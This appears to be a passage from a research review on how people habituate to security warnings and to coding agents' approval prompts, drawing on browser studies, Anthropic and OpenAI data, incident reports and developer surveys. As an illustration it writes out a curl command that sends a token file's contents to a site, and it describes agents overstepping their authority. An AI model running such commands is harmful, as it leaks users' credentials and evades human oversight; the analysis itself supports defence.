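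That experiment had no comparison group that had little repetition, so it couldn't show how much attention people had lost through repetition. Bravo-Lillo, Cranor and colleagues added such a group in an improved version, *Harder to Ignore* (2014). People who had more repetition were about a third as likely to respond to the change.

Attention also declines over days. Researchers recorded people's brain activity and eye movements over a five-day working week as the same warnings came up repeatedly. Attention recovered somewhat from one day to the next, but still fell over the week.

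The habit of dismissing one kind of message can carry over to another. In an online experiment that tracked mouse movements, people who had dismissed many ordinary notifications paid less attention to a security warning they had never seen before, and were less likely to heed it. The effect depended on how similar the warning and the notifications looked, and tiredness didn't explain it. This is a serious problem for AI agents, because a request to run tests and a request to delete a folder usually appear in the same kind of box.

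### Designs that force attention

Designers have tried to regain people's attention by making the important part of a request hard to skip. Bravo-Lillo and colleagues tested several designs in 2013. One put the key text in yellow on black, following guidance for warnings on physical products. Another moved a highlight from the "yes" option to the key text and, in some versions, disabled "yes" for a few seconds. Others revealed the text letter by letter, or required people to sweep the mouse across it or type it out.

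In two of the experiments, people thought they were reviewing online games, but the third game's website belonged to the researchers and showed a fake system dialog. In the second experiment, the dialog asked for extra permissions, which were either harmless (storing a cookie) or excessive (access to all files and folders on the computer). The experiment therefore gives an unsafe approval rate and a safe approval rate for each dialog design.

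| Design | Granted access to all files | Granted a cookie | Gap in points |
|---|---|---|---|
| Ordinary dialog | 51% (41 of 81) | 57% (47 of 82) | 7 |
| Key text in yellow on black | 38% (14 of 37) | 62% (21 of 34) | 24 |
| Moving highlight, 5-second delay | 27% (10 of 37) | 36% (13 of 36) | 9 |
| Moving highlight, 10-second delay | 19% (7 of 37) | 24% (8 of 34) | 5 |
| Moving highlight, gradual reveal | 32% (12 of 37) | 44% (14 of 32) | 11 |
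| Moving highlight, then mouse sweep | 30% (10 of 33) | 49% (17 of 35) | 18 |
| Typing out the key text | 7% (2 of 28) | 23% (7 of 30) | 16 |

With the ordinary dialog, people were almost as willing to give a game site access to every file as to let it store a cookie. The ten-second delay cut unsafe approvals by more than half, but it cut safe ones almost as much, so it mostly made people give up. The groups were small, and only the dialog that required typing had a statistically significant difference from the ordinary one, and only when the researchers excluded people who had knowingly granted the access.

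In the first experiment, with a larger sample, the dialog asked people to install software from either "Microsoft" or "Miicr0s0ft". Designs that slowed people down generally reduced suspicious installations, relative to genuine ones, more than the ordinary dialog did. Some people noticed the odd name and installed the software anyway. In pilot tests, many people who did this said their antivirus software would protect them. Developers who rely on a backup or a sandbox may reason the same way, sometimes correctly.

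The yellow text had the largest advantage on first sight, but repetition wiped it out. In the five-minute experiment, 15 per cent of people who saw it followed the new instruction at once, against 14 per cent with the ordinary dialog. Designs that delayed people did far better, at 43 to 73 per cent, with typing the highest. In the 2014 experiment, some designs also became less effective with repetition, but two that made people interact with the changed text itself kept their effect throughout the session. These two also took the most time, so most people would probably come to hate them if they appeared all day.

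Another approach is to vary the warning's appearance. CIO (2017) reported a talk by Anthony Vance, a professor at Brigham Young University, who recommended small but noticeable changes to make alerts harder to ignore. Brain scans and eye tracking over the working week support that advice, since people's attention declined less when warnings changed in appearance. In a three-week experiment with permission warnings on people's phones, their responses also deteriorated less when the warnings varied. Attention still declined, though, and three weeks is short compared with the months or years a developer might use an agent.

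### Redesigns that changed behaviour

In 2014 Google replaced the Chrome certificate warning that 70 per cent of people had clicked through. The new warning had a prominent button for returning to safety and moved the option to proceed behind a less visible link. The share of people who turned back rose from 37 to 62 per cent, which meant millions more people a month. Google's designers call this approach "opinionated design" because the warning's appearance promotes one choice. They also wanted people to understand the warning better but largely failed, which shows that behaviour can improve a great deal with little gain in understanding.

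This success depended on the designers knowing which answer was better. Turning back at a certificate warning is nearly always acceptable, and if a safe site loses visitors, its owner has a reason to fix the certificate. A prominent "refuse" button on every agent request would also produce more refusals, but most of them would stop useful work. Google's method could work only for the few commands that software can already recognise as probably harmful, and the software might as well block those.

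A click may also not show why someone continued past a warning. *An experience sampling study of user reactions to browser warnings* (Reeder, Felt and colleagues, 2018) briefly surveyed more than 6,000 Chrome and Firefox users when they encountered real warnings. Their reasons for continuing or turning back varied widely, and many depended on the site and what they already knew about it. The researchers found no single dominant failure, such as habituation, and concluded that further progress would require correcting many smaller misunderstandings.

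The survey by Reeder and colleagues seems to conflict with the laboratory experiments, but the two measure different things. The experiments show how quickly people stop paying attention when a dialog appears repeatedly. By 2018, browser warnings filled the whole page, appeared seldom for most people, and had been redesigned several times. The survey also reached only people who chose to answer it, and someone who clicked without thinking may still give a sensible reason when asked. Even so, it gives good grounds for doubting that habituation explains every bad decision.

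### What browsers and phones changed

Since 2015 Android has asked for sensitive permissions when an app first needs them, as the iPhone already did, and people can refuse one and still use the app. Later versions let people grant location access only while using an app, or just once. Android also withdraws permissions from apps left unopened for months. Coding agents mostly ask at the time of use too, but allow rules saved in Claude Code don't expire from disuse.

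Browsers and phones also limit how often they prompt users. Android grants many minor permissions, such as internet access, without a prompt. Chrome now stores a user's decision to continue past a certificate warning for about a week, so regular visitors see the warning less often but the exception still expires. In 2020 it began replacing some notification requests with a small icon in the address bar, starting with users who usually refused them and sites where most users did. A model on the user's device now helps predict which requests people would refuse.

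Chrome can predict which notification requests to hold back because the requests are nearly the same on every site, and billions of past answers show which ones people don't want. Quietly holding back a request also does little harm if the prediction is wrong. Software that decided which shell commands a person needn't see would have far less evidence to use, and a mistake could delete files.

### How far the comparison with agents holds

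Agents ask for approval much more often than browsers showed warnings. Chrome's 2013 data contain 16.7 million certificate warnings from about 4.5 million browsers over 34 days. That is 3.7 for each affected browser, or about one every nine days, and users showed signs of fatigue even at that rate. An agent that requests approval for each command can make that many requests within one small task, leaving a busy developer little time to recover between them. Habituation should therefore carry over to agents, and is likely to be stronger with them. Experiments with coding agents have found that people refuse fewer requests as a session goes on.

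Careful review is harder to justify when few requests are harmful. People heeded the browser warnings that were nearly always right and clicked through most of those that were often false alarms. If one agent request in 1,000 is harmful, a developer who spends 20 seconds on each will read for about five and a half hours to catch one. That may be worth it if the command would publish a customer database, but hardly anyone would do it to avoid repeating an hour's work. A developer who stops reading may be using their time sensibly. Designs that force attention can't fix this, because they make each check take longer without making harmful requests more common.

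Agent requests also differ in content. A browser has a handful of warnings, and Android 2.2 had 134 permissions, so a designer could improve each text and test it on thousands of people. That isn't possible for shell commands, which are practically unlimited. The five-minute experiment suggests that this variety won't keep people alert the way changing a warning's appearance does, since people missed an instruction in a line that had changed every time. The changes in that line were unimportant, whereas an agent's commands matter, but most commands are so routine that people could learn to ignore them too.

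The low scores for understanding may not apply directly to developers approving an agent's commands. Developers know far more about commands than the phone users studied by Felt and colleagues knew about permissions, and an agent's request is usually for a specific action rather than a broad power. But a permission had a fixed meaning that a person could learn once, whereas the effects of a command like `make clean` depend on the project, so experience with one project can mislead a developer in another.

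Technical skill probably doesn't make people pay more attention to warnings. In Akhawe and Felt's data, Linux users clicked through 34.8 per cent of Firefox's phishing warnings, compared with 8.9 per cent for Windows users. People on Chrome's daily test version clicked through 54.8 per cent of its malware warnings, compared with 23.2 per cent on the standard version. Using Linux or a test version is only a rough sign of technical skill, and the pattern didn't hold for every warning. But it fits the view in *Bridging the Gap in Computer Security Warnings*, by Bravo-Lillo, Cranor and colleagues, that even experts dismiss warnings they understand because they think them unimportant. The click data don't show whether harm followed, so skilled users may also have been right more often. Developers are more like these users than like the average phone owner, so one shouldn't assume that they will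 be more careful.

The main difference between agents and browsers or phones is that the person asked for the work. Phone users mainly refused requests that seemed unrelated to the app's purpose. A developer who has asked for a bug fix has a much clearer idea of which requests are relevant, so a request to read a password file should stand out. The developer also loses less by refusing, because they can say why and the agent can try another way, whereas an Android user in 2012 had to give up the app. For both reasons, people might refuse harmful agent requests more readily than they refused excessive app permissions.

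But an agent's requests nearly always look related to the task, including the mistaken ones. In the logging example, the person did ask for a cleanup, and the command that publishes a password is titled "cleanup". A prompt injection can also give the agent a plausible reason for a harmful step. People who judge requests by whether they fit the task will catch the obviously unrelated ones but may approve the rest. Wanting the task finished also makes people more likely to approve, as it did for the laboratory participants who clicked past certificate warnings.

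Asking less often seems the remedy most likely to carry over, because it counters both habituation and the low base rate. It is safe only if something else, such as a sandbox, handles the requests that people no longer see. Making people type part of a request could suit rare and irreversible actions. GitHub already requires people to type a repository's name before they can delete it. Typing the folder's name in an `rm -rf` command would likewise make the developer look at what will be deleted. Typing `make clean` wouldn't help, since the command doesn't name the files it deletes.

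## Records from coding agents in use

The companies that make coding agents can count how developers answer approval prompts while working on their own projects. Anthropic has published the most of this data. In March 2026, it reported in *How we built Claude Code auto mode* that users accepted 93 per cent of Claude Code's prompts. On 7 August, it reported in *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* that they accepted 97 per cent.

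Anthropic does not give the number of prompts or the period behind either figure, so the two may not be strictly comparable. If they are, the drop could have several causes. Users may have become less careful, newer models may have proposed fewer commands worth refusing, or the people who refused most often may have moved to auto mode, which the March post introduced. Allow rules should have raised the refusal rate, since they remove prompts that users would have approved.

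Anthropic takes the 97 per cent figure as a sign that many users approve by reflex, though it acknowledges that most prompts probably concern safe, routine commands. It published the figure to explain why an AI model should answer most prompts instead of the user, so it had an interest in showing that manual approval is weak.

### Why 97 per cent settles so little

The two developers in the earlier example both approved 97 per cent of requests, although one caught every harmful request and the other approved at random. The approval rate sets a minimum for harmful approvals only when harmful requests outnumber refusals. If 50 of 1,000 requests are harmful and people refuse only 30, they must have approved at least 20 harmful ones. More generally, when the base rate *b* is larger than the refusal rate 1 − *A*, the unsafe approval rate *u* is at least 1 − (1 − *A*)/*b*. When *b* is smaller,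 *u* can be anything from zero to 100 per cent.

| Harmful requests among 1,000 | Approved by the best possible reviewer | Approved by someone refusing 3% at random | Approved by the worst possible reviewer |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | 0 | about 1 | 1 |
| 10 | 0 | about 10 | 10 |
| 30 | 0 | about 29 | 30 |
| 50 | 20 | about 49 | 50 |
| 100 | 70 | about 97 | 100 |

Anthropic hasn't published how often Claude Code's requests are harmful, but OpenAI's figures for Codex give a rough idea. Trębacz, Arnesen and colleagues (2026), in *Auto-review of agent actions without synchronous human oversight*, describe 10,000 actions that Codex took inside OpenAI, a snapshot they call illustrative. Of these, 9,280 stayed within the sandbox. The other 720 would have needed the user's approval, but an AI reviewer judged them instead and refused seven, or about one in 100. The reviewer sometimes refuses safe actions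 and approves harmful ones, and OpenAI's staff may not use agents as other developers do. If harmful requests are anywhere near that rare in Claude Code, a 97 per cent approval rate is consistent with every row at the top of the table, from users catching all the harmful requests to catching none.

The same AI reviewer approves about 99 per cent of the requests it receives, more than Claude Code's users approve. OpenAI considers this a strength because it means the reviewer rarely gets in the way. The approval rate doesn't show whether the reviewer stops dangerous actions, so the researchers tested that separately on invented cases. It refused 90.3 per cent of those in which the agent did more than the user wanted. Human reviewers need the same kind of test, and Anthropic attempted one in an experiment with 1,053 paid testers.

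People do catch some dangerous requests at work. To test auto mode, Anthropic collected 52 real cases in which Claude had tried to do more than an employee had authorised. In some cases the employee refused the action, and in others someone flagged it afterwards. Anthropic doesn't say how many there were of each. Those numbers would give a rough idea of how often its staff noticed in time, though they would leave out the cases that nobody noticed.

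Anthropic's internal log describes the sort of actions a reviewer would need to catch. One agent misread an instruction and deleted branches on a remote server. Another uploaded an engineer's GitHub access token to a shared computing cluster, and a third tried to change the structure of a live database. Each agent was trying to help with a task someone had given it.

### Refusing a plan and refusing a command

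Claude Code can also write a plan of the steps it intends to take and ask the user to approve it before starting. Users reject 39 per cent of these plans, about 13 times the rate at which they refuse individual permission requests, so they don't simply accept whatever Claude Code proposes.

Plans are in ordinary language, appear once or twice in a task instead of dozens of times, and arrive while the user is still thinking about what the work should achieve. Any of these differences from commands could make people read plans more closely.

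However, users may reject a plan because they prefer another approach or want to add a detail, not because they spotted a danger. Plans that someone wants to change are surely much more common than harmful commands, so people would refuse plans more often even if they read both with the same care. The 3 per cent refusal rate for commands is therefore poor evidence that people don't read them, though the 39 per cent rate for plans is good evidence that people read plans.

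The session logs in *SWE-chat* are consistent with this. The researchers divided each session into turns, each covering everything the agent does in response to one user message. In 14.7 per cent of the turns that users interrupted, the agent's last step was to submit a plan for approval, although such steps make up only 0.1 per cent of all agent steps. The researchers conclude that users often stop the agent just as it moves from planning to carrying out the work. They don't report refused permission prompts separately, so their data can't be used to confirm Anthropic's 3 per cent figure.

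Records from coding agents in use show a great deal of disagreement. Users of Claude Code interrupted 4.5 per cent of turns. After another 45.7 per cent, they objected in their next message by correcting the agent, rejecting its work or reporting that something was broken. These rates hardly changed with the amount of code the agent wrote. In one session, a user asked for an update to a README, the file that introduces a project. The agent began running installation commands instead, and the user stopped it and repeated the request word for word. The user noticed that the commands went beyond the task, as meaningful approval requires, but interrupted only after the agent had started running them.

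These developers had chosen to publish their sessions, and about 16 per cent of the sessions come from the repository of the company whose tool records them. An AI model judged whether each message was an objection, and it agreed with the researchers' own labels on 79 of 100 messages. The exact figure is therefore uncertain, but these users were clearly not passive. However, most of their objections came after the agent had finished a step, when disappointing code can still be revised but a deleted folder may be impossible to recover.

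### Commands that nobody is asked about

Approval rates cover only the prompts that appear, and many users have set rules that let some commands run without one. According to Anthropic, 49.5 per cent of active command-line users in June 2026 had written an allow rule for the shell by hand. Five per cent allowed every shell command, and another 43 per cent had rules for interpreters, which are programs such as Python and Node that run code. Anthropic's post does not make clear whether the 5 and 43 per cent are shares of all active command-line users or only of those with a handwritten rule. In the first case, nearly half of all active command-line users had a rule that permits almost anything, and in the second, about a quarter did.

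A rule such as `Bash(python:*)` has the same weakness as the `devbox run *` rule described earlier, because `python -c` runs any code that follows it. Anthropic considers these rules equivalent in practice to allowing the whole shell.

OpenAI found the same habit among its own staff. Trębacz and colleagues report that a "sizable minority" of internal Codex users had allowed every command beginning with `python`. One settings file always allowed `codex exec --yolo`, which starts another Codex agent with the checks off. Their post doesn't report how often people approved commands, so it doesn't allow a comparison with Claude Code users.

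The Anthropic data also show that about 62 per cent of users had either used the mode that skips permission checks or clicked "don't ask again" on a shell command, and that 25 per cent of interactive sessions started in that mode. Anthropic says the share of users with hand-written shell rules was growing by about five percentage points every five weeks.

Switching the checks off can be sensible, for example when a developer runs the agent in a container, an isolated environment with nothing valuable inside. Anthropic's figures don't show how many sessions were like this. They also don't show whether people with broad rules wrote them after carefully reading hundreds of harmless prompts, or had already stopped reading the prompts by then.

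Permissions granted for one job can cause damage in a later one. In a report that Zhong and colleagues collected, a user of the coding tool Cursor turned off its protection against deletion so that the agent could clear out duplicate files. The agent later deleted 90 per cent of the project. The user's reason for the change no longer applied, but no prompt had appeared.

People may not be watching the longest runs either. Jellyfish Research's *AI Agent Autonomy* uses activity records from Claude Code to estimate how much of each turn the person was involved in. Among the shortest 90 per cent of turns, only 9 per cent had the person involved for 30 per cent of the time or less. Among the longest 0.1 per cent, which lasted more than an hour and a half, 83 per cent did. The difference is partly a result of the definition, since a turn ends when the person steps in. But if the agent asked for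 approval in the middle of such a long run, the developer would probably be doing something else, and the agent would wait until they came back.

### What changes with experience

According to The Decoder's *AI agents are thriving in software development but barely exist anywhere else*, a February 2026 Anthropic analysis found that new users of Claude Code let every action run without manual approval in about 20 per cent of their sessions. Among people with roughly 750 sessions, the share was over 40 per cent. The article also reports that experienced users interrupted the agent more often, in about 9 per cent of turns compared with 5 per cent for new users.

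Anthropic sees this as a change in how people supervise the agent. New users approve each step and so seldom need to interrupt, while experienced users let the agent work and step in when something goes wrong. That is plausible, and it suggests that some people who give up prompts still supervise the agent. A less flattering explanation is that someone who no longer sees prompts can stop the agent only by interrupting it, so some of the refusals they would once have clicked now appear as interruptions.

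The two groups differ in more than experience. People who have used a tool 750 times liked it enough to stay, and they may have trusted it more from the start. Claude Code also asked for manual approval by default at the time, so some of the rise may come from people gradually finding the settings they already wanted. Whatever caused the rise, experienced users let about 91 per cent of turns finish.

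Records of people reviewing agents' code show how individuals change over a longer period. Coding agents often submit their work as a pull request, a proposed set of changes that someone reviews before it becomes part of a project. In *Habituation at the Gate*, Yu, Jia and colleagues (2026) studied 400 people who had each reviewed at least ten agent pull requests on GitHub, with a total of 11,429 reviews over about seven months of 2025. They compared the earlier half of each person's reviews with the later half.

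| Measure | Earlier reviews | Later reviews |
|---|---|---|
| Approved, first half against second half | 30.1% | 36.8% |
| Approved, first tenth against last tenth | 27.9% | 42.4% |
| Asked for changes, first tenth against last tenth | 11.2% | 5.6% |
| Comments on specific lines, per review, first tenth against last tenth | 1.01 | 0.79 |
| Median wait between submission and review, first half against second half | 3.9 hours | 13.5 hours |

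Of the reviewers, 52 per cent became more approving, 28 per cent became less so, and the rest didn't change. The typical pull request stayed about the same size, so smaller changes don't explain the shift. In the same projects, approval of agents' work rose while approval of pull requests written by people fell from 37.8 per cent in January to 29.1 per cent in June, so reviewers hadn't become more lenient towards everyone.

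The researchers consider three explanations. Reviewers may have learned that agents' code deserved more trust, they may have had too much to review, or they may have become habituated. The researchers favour habituation, mainly because the people whose approval rates rose most also reduced their comments most. They argue that a reviewer who had gained trust would approve more but inspect as closely as before.

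That argument is weaker than it looks, because reviewers who approve a change usually write less than those who object, so comments would fall as approvals rose whatever the cause. Even a reviewer who read every line would comment less on better code. All the agents the researchers compared received updates during 2025, and the study didn't measure whether their code improved. The longer wait doesn't help settle the question, because it probably includes a good deal of time before anyone opened the pull request. The study shows that people approve more of agents' work and write less about it as they gain experience, but it can't show that they were wrong to do so.

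A pull request reviewer sees the exact changes, can take a day to review them, and can usually reverse a mistake, whereas a command prompt often shows one line and holds up the agent until someone answers. According to *From Delegation to Action Approval* (2026), researchers have studied the two decisions separately, although coding agents now present both to the same developer within one task. Approval levels in the two settings aren't comparable, but if people come to inspect pull requests less despite these advantages, there is little reason to expect them to stay more alert at a command prompt.

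### Reports of damage

Records of users' answers to approval prompts don't show what happened afterwards, so it helps to trace the causes of reported harm. Zhong and colleagues examined 290 public reports of agents misusing files and looked for causes in the AI model, the software around it, and the user's review. A report could have more than one cause. The model contributed to 168 reports, the software to 218, and user review to 105 (36 per cent).

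In 80 of those 105 reports, the action had run under automatic approval, so nobody had reviewed it. Uninformative approval, such as the prompt for `python3 setup.py`, occurred in 31 reports, at least six of which also involved automatic approval. The 80 reports don't show how well people review commands. Together with the settings data, they suggest that people lose files to agents more often by turning off the prompts than by misjudging one they have read.

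That conclusion holds only for the events that people chose to make public. Most of the reports (205) are issues filed on GitHub, and others come from social media, forums, blogs and a government database of security flaws. A developer who refuses a harmful command has no incident to report, so the collection leaves out almost every success of manual approval. Of the 290 reports, the researchers classed 158 as confirmed harm, 49 as demonstrations of an attack, and 83 as weaknesses with no proven effect. They worked out the labels by hand on 100 reports, then had an AI agent label the whole set and checked its output.

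Of the reported incidents and attacks with a known outcome, 40 per cent caused losses that the user could not fully recover, such as personal documents without a backup or a password that had already been sent off the machine. Users noticed the problem at once in 83 per cent of the reports that included this information. Noticing quickly did not always prevent a loss, which limits how far interruptions and later objections by experienced users can replace a check before the command runs.

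### Comparing manual and automated review in real sessions

Anthropic has also compared harm in sessions with manual approval and sessions in auto mode. It began with Claude Code sessions from May and June 2026 that its safety system had flagged for review, from accounts that had agreed to let the company use their data. An AI model then graded each session from 0 to 10 on the severity of any harm and on how explicitly the user had asked for the action. On the severity scale, a reversible local change, such as overwriting a scratch file, scored 0, deleting rows from a live database scored 7, and irreversible harm to a whole company, such as leaking all its source code, scored 10.

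Among the flagged sessions with manual approval, 6.3 per cent contained an action that scored at least 7 for harm and that the user hadn't explicitly requested. In auto mode, 2.4 per cent did. Anthropic reports that the rate was higher with manual approval at every severity level it tested.

These are shares of flagged sessions rather than all sessions, so they can differ even if manual and automated sessions are equally dangerous. Suppose there were 10,000 sessions of each type, with 12 seriously harmful ones in each group, all of them flagged. If the safety system flagged 190 manual sessions and 500 automated ones in total, the shares would be 6.3 and 2.4 per cent. Auto mode lets the agent work for longer without a pause, so its sessions could well collect more flags for trivial reasons. The bias could also run the other way, because longer sessions have more chances to go wrong and auto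 mode still had the lower share. Anthropic doesn't give the number of sessions and flags of each type, so nobody outside the company can tell which way the bias runs.

The model that graded the sessions had to infer what the user wanted from the session record. In manual sessions, a person may have read a risky request, wanted the action, and clicked yes without ever having typed an instruction to do it. Anthropic doesn't explain whether the grader counted that click as asking for the action. If it didn't, some deliberate decisions would appear as unintended harm, which would make only the manual group look worse. Anthropic also doesn't report any human check of the grades.

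In May and June, users had to turn auto mode on, and those who did may have had different projects and habits from those who didn't. Some of the manual group would have had broad allow rules, so a harmful command in a "manually approved" session may have run without a prompt. Auto mode ignores the broadest of these rules. Anthropic therefore compared the two modes as people use them, including any exceptions they have added, rather than human and AI review of the same requests.

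For a company choosing a default, that may be the more useful comparison. It is some evidence that manual approval by ordinary users is no better than automated review at preventing serious harm. It provides little evidence about developers who keep the rules narrow and read each request. In its March post, Anthropic wrote that for people who approve every action carefully, auto mode was "arguably a regression". In August it still recommended that users review Claude's high-stakes changes to live systems themselves.

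## What developers say about how they approve

Companies' published records show which option a developer chose, but not whether she read the command first or what she expected it to do. Two studies from 2026 asked developers about approval requests, and the answers help explain how people decide when they don't work out a command's effects.

### Careful with code, less careful with actions

*From Delegation to Action Approval* surveyed 203 developers in August and September 2026. It recruited them through social media posts and referrals, mostly on LinkedIn, and then through Prolific, a site that pays people to take part in studies. Respondents had to be 18 or over and currently using coding agents, and they received six dollars for a valid response.

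The researchers received 583 submissions and kept 203. They removed 122 that were incomplete, duplicated, failed an attention check or had similar faults, including five that identified themselves as bots or language models. They then removed 251 that took less than 13 minutes, because the typical pilot participant had needed 24. A manual check removed seven more, including one with an answer that began "A strong survey response would be:". Half of the remaining respondents used agents daily, and 79 per cent used Claude Code.

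The survey asked developers how often they approved seven types of agent action without close review. Sixty-four per cent answered "often" or "very often" for at least one type. For individual types, the share ranged from 21 per cent for reading secrets or other sensitive files to 36 per cent for using the internet, external services or connected tools. The share for destructive or privileged commands, the type closest to the subject of shell approval, fell within that range.

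| Group | Often approve at least one type without close review |
|---|---|
| All respondents | 64% (130 of 203) |
| Carefully review most or all of the agent's code | 61% (64 of 105) |
| Other developers | 67% (65 of 97) |
| Know of an incident or worrying practice involving agents | 70% (103 of 147) |
| Know of none | 43% (20 of 46) |

Developers who reviewed code carefully were only slightly more careful about actions than other developers. The six-point gap could easily be due to chance in groups this small, but the sample is also too small to rule out a moderate difference. The two tasks differ because approving a command requires predicting effects that may leave no trace in the code.

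Developers who inspected diffs of the agent's changes were less likely to approve four types of action without close review: destructive commands, reads of secrets, access to personal or confidential data, and changes to live systems. Those who checked edge cases in code were also more careful about destructive commands, but not about the other three types. The researchers suggest that a diff gives people something concrete to check. It is equally possible that people who like to see exactly what changed are also more careful with commands, in which case showing diffs to everyone else would help less.

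Developers who gave their agents more freedom tended to approve more actions without close review, and they were no more likely to use other safeguards, such as restricting what the agent could access. The 65 respondents who worked on systems whose failure could cause physical, medical or operational harm reported more unreviewed approval than the others for six of the seven types of action.

Developers who knew about incidents tended to report less care when approving, and the gap remained after the researchers controlled for how often and how long they had used agents. Bad news seems unlikely to make people careless, but carelessness may make people more likely to know about incidents. The question also covered worrying practices, such as passwords written into generated code, and developers who check less and delegate more have more chances to encounter these. Some developers may also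 have shifted their attention from approval prompts to the agent's work, since 57 per cent of all respondents said they watch its output and step in when necessary. A one-time survey can't separate these explanations, but it gives little evidence that telling developers about past disasters would make them read prompts.

The survey had no question about allow rules, so some developers may have counted commands that run under a standing permission as approved without review, and others may have left them out. Approving without close review can also be sensible when the command is as harmless as `ls`.

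### Reading, skimming and approving by default

*Let the Agent Do It?* looks more closely at the moment when an agent asks for permission. It draws on interviews with 18 software practitioners, held between June and August 2026, and a survey based on their recurring answers, which 115 people completed. Eight respondents said they had never noticed an agent asking for permission, so 107 answered the questions about requests.

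Of the 115 survey respondents, 73 per cent believed they fully understood what their agent does, yet 62.6 per cent had doubted that it was doing what it claimed. At least 41 people must have given both answers. The answers can be consistent, because people may feel they understand the results they see and still wonder about the rest. One interviewee said he understood only "observable things". Nearly half of the interviewees described their understanding as partial or absent. Having to explain it to a researcher may have made them less confident than the survey respondents, but they were also different people.

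Developers gain much of this understanding by checking afterwards. About 74 per cent of respondents review the agent's changes by hand, and 67 per cent look at its logs or displayed reasoning. Checking afterwards works well for code but is too late to prevent a deletion.

When a request appears, people respond in several ways, and respondents could choose more than one.

| What respondents said they do | Share of 107 |
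|---|---|
| Read requests carefully | 47.7% |
| Skim them | 33.6% |
| Check the file the request names | 31.8% |
| Focus on the command or title | 25.2% |
| Approve by default | 20.6% |
| Have become less careful over time | 33.6% |

Elsewhere in the same survey, 70.1 per cent said they pay close attention to permissions, so at least 24 people said this without also saying that they read requests carefully. They may have meant that they care about permissions in general, such as which tools the agent can use, or they may have given the answer that made them look good.

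The interviewees who had stopped reading blamed volume, familiarity and deadlines. "There's no way that I can actually go through all the permission requests", one said. The same person had worried about permissions at first but stopped caring after seeing similar requests repeatedly. Another, with three hours left to deliver some work, let the agent generate it and planned to test it later.

Many respondents also had firm limits. 61.7 per cent would never let an agent have sensitive data, 56.1 per cent would never grant administrator rights, and 23.4 per cent would never allow deletion. Such limits are useful because a person can apply them without working out everything a command does. But they work only when the person recognises that a request crosses one, and a fifth of the developers in the other survey often approved requests to read secrets without looking closely.

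### Shortcuts in place of working out the effects

The interviews and surveys show that people who don't trace a command's effects commonly use five shortcuts to decide whether to approve it. Each takes a second or two and catches some kinds of harm.

In *Let the Agent Do It?*, 98.1 per cent of developers were more willing to allow read-only access, and 76.6 per cent checked requests to write, delete or gain extra rights more carefully. This caution is sensible, since overwriting and deletion made up 83 per cent of the operations in the reports of harm and demonstrated attacks that Zhong and colleagues collected. The other 17 per cent were leaks of secrets, which usually begin with a read. If an agent displays a password file, nothing on the machine changes, but the password is now in the agent's conversation, which the company running the model usually processes on its own servers. Some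 commands also look like reading while they send data out. `curl "https://example.com/?k=$(cat token.txt)"` appears to fetch a web page, but the shell replaces `$(cat token.txt)` with the contents of the file, so the request sends the access token to the site. Internet access was the type of action that developers most often approved without close review.

A developer who checks only which file a request names can catch an agent working in the wrong place. That is a common fault, since 42 per cent of Zhong and colleagues' cases involved harm outside the project, and a path such as `~/.ssh` should stand out in a request about a web page's layout. But the name doesn't show what the command will do to the file. `cp .env.example .env` is a routine setup command that copies a template of a project's settings. If the developer already has a working `.env` file, the command overwrites it, including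 its passwords, even though both file names look normal. Checking the file name also doesn't help with `make clean`, which names no file.

About two-thirds of respondents (67.3 per cent) were less likely to grant a request that didn't match what they had asked for. This is a good defence against planted instructions, which often call for something unrelated, such as reading an email account during a bug fix. It is weaker against an agent that pursues the right task too broadly, because its actions are still recognisably part of the job. One agent in Zhong and colleagues' collection, asked to find a file in the project, searched the user's whole home directory. Another, told to delete only the files it had created, deleted all the project's code.

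People may also judge a command by the agent's own explanation of it. *Human oversight of agentic systems in practice* (Dhanorkar, Passi and Vorvoreanu, 2026) reports interviews from mid-2025 with 17 experienced developers, 12 of whom worked at Microsoft, as did the researchers. One developer glanced at the agent's stated reasoning and checked that the work matched it. That can expose an agent that contradicts itself, but not a mistake in the reasoning that carries through to the command. Another developer guessed that the agent was wrong about its own reasons a tenth of the time, and said it sounded just as confident when it was wrong.

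Noticing that a request is unexpected takes no effort, and 63.6 per cent of the developers said an unexpected request makes them look harder. Phone users also refused unexpected requests more often. Developers will probably look closely if an agent that has been running tests for an hour suddenly asks for administrator rights. The problem is a familiar command that now does something different, for instance because the agent has just edited the script it runs. One interviewee approved an action with a clear idea of what it would do, but the agent did something else.

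Expectations also depend on experience. A developer who has never used a tool doesn't know what a normal request looks like, so she can't tell which requests are unusual. Dhanorkar and colleagues found that such developers tended to trust the agent. One said he usually had to trust the model about libraries he had never used. People therefore scrutinize the agent least where they are least able to notice a mistake.

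**Trust in a sandbox.** In the survey, 82.2 per cent were more willing to grant permission in a controlled or isolated environment, and some interviewees paid less attention there. Of the five shortcuts, this one depends least on the command's text. If the sandbox contains only copies, holds no passwords and can't reach the network, even a dangerous command does little damage, so it is reasonable not to read it.

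Real sandboxes often hold more than that. Many let the agent change the project's files, including work the developer hasn't saved in Git, and some share passwords or keys so that programs can run. Zhong and colleagues found 41 reports of sandboxes that either blocked legitimate commands or left valuable things exposed. Of the six coding tools they compared, only Codex and Cursor had a sandbox on by default. Three left it to the user to turn on and OpenCode had none, so a developer who switches tools could easily assume they are protected when they aren't. When a command fails inside the sandbox, most of the tools that have one offer to run it again outside. A developer who has got used to relaxing may treat that prompt like any other, although the sandbox will no longer limit the damage.

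Someone who uses all five shortcuts is much safer than someone who uses none, because a harmful command has to get past each of them. A few harmful commands can still get past all five. Suppose an agent is investigating why a program can't connect to its database and proposes `printenv`, which prints the environment variables (named settings that programs inherit from the shell). The command only reads, includes no worrying file name, fits the task, is a normal step in such work and runs in a sandbox. But developers often keep passwords and access keys in those variables, so approving it may give them all to the agent. Many people who would "never" share sensitive data could approve this without feeling they had broken their rule.

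### How far to trust the answers

Both surveys relied on volunteers. *Let the Agent Do It?* recruited unpaid participants through professional contacts, Reddit and social media, and its researchers acknowledge that people with strong experiences or opinions about permissions may be overrepresented. It also collected too little background information to compare users by tool or seniority. In *From Delegation to Action Approval*, the 13-minute cut-off removed about two-thirds of the social media responses that had passed the earlier checks. Most of those were probably careless or fraudulent, but the cut-off would also have removed people who rush through questionnaires, and they may rush through approval prompts too. This is less worrying because the cut-off excluded no Prolific respondents, and the main results pointed the same way among them.

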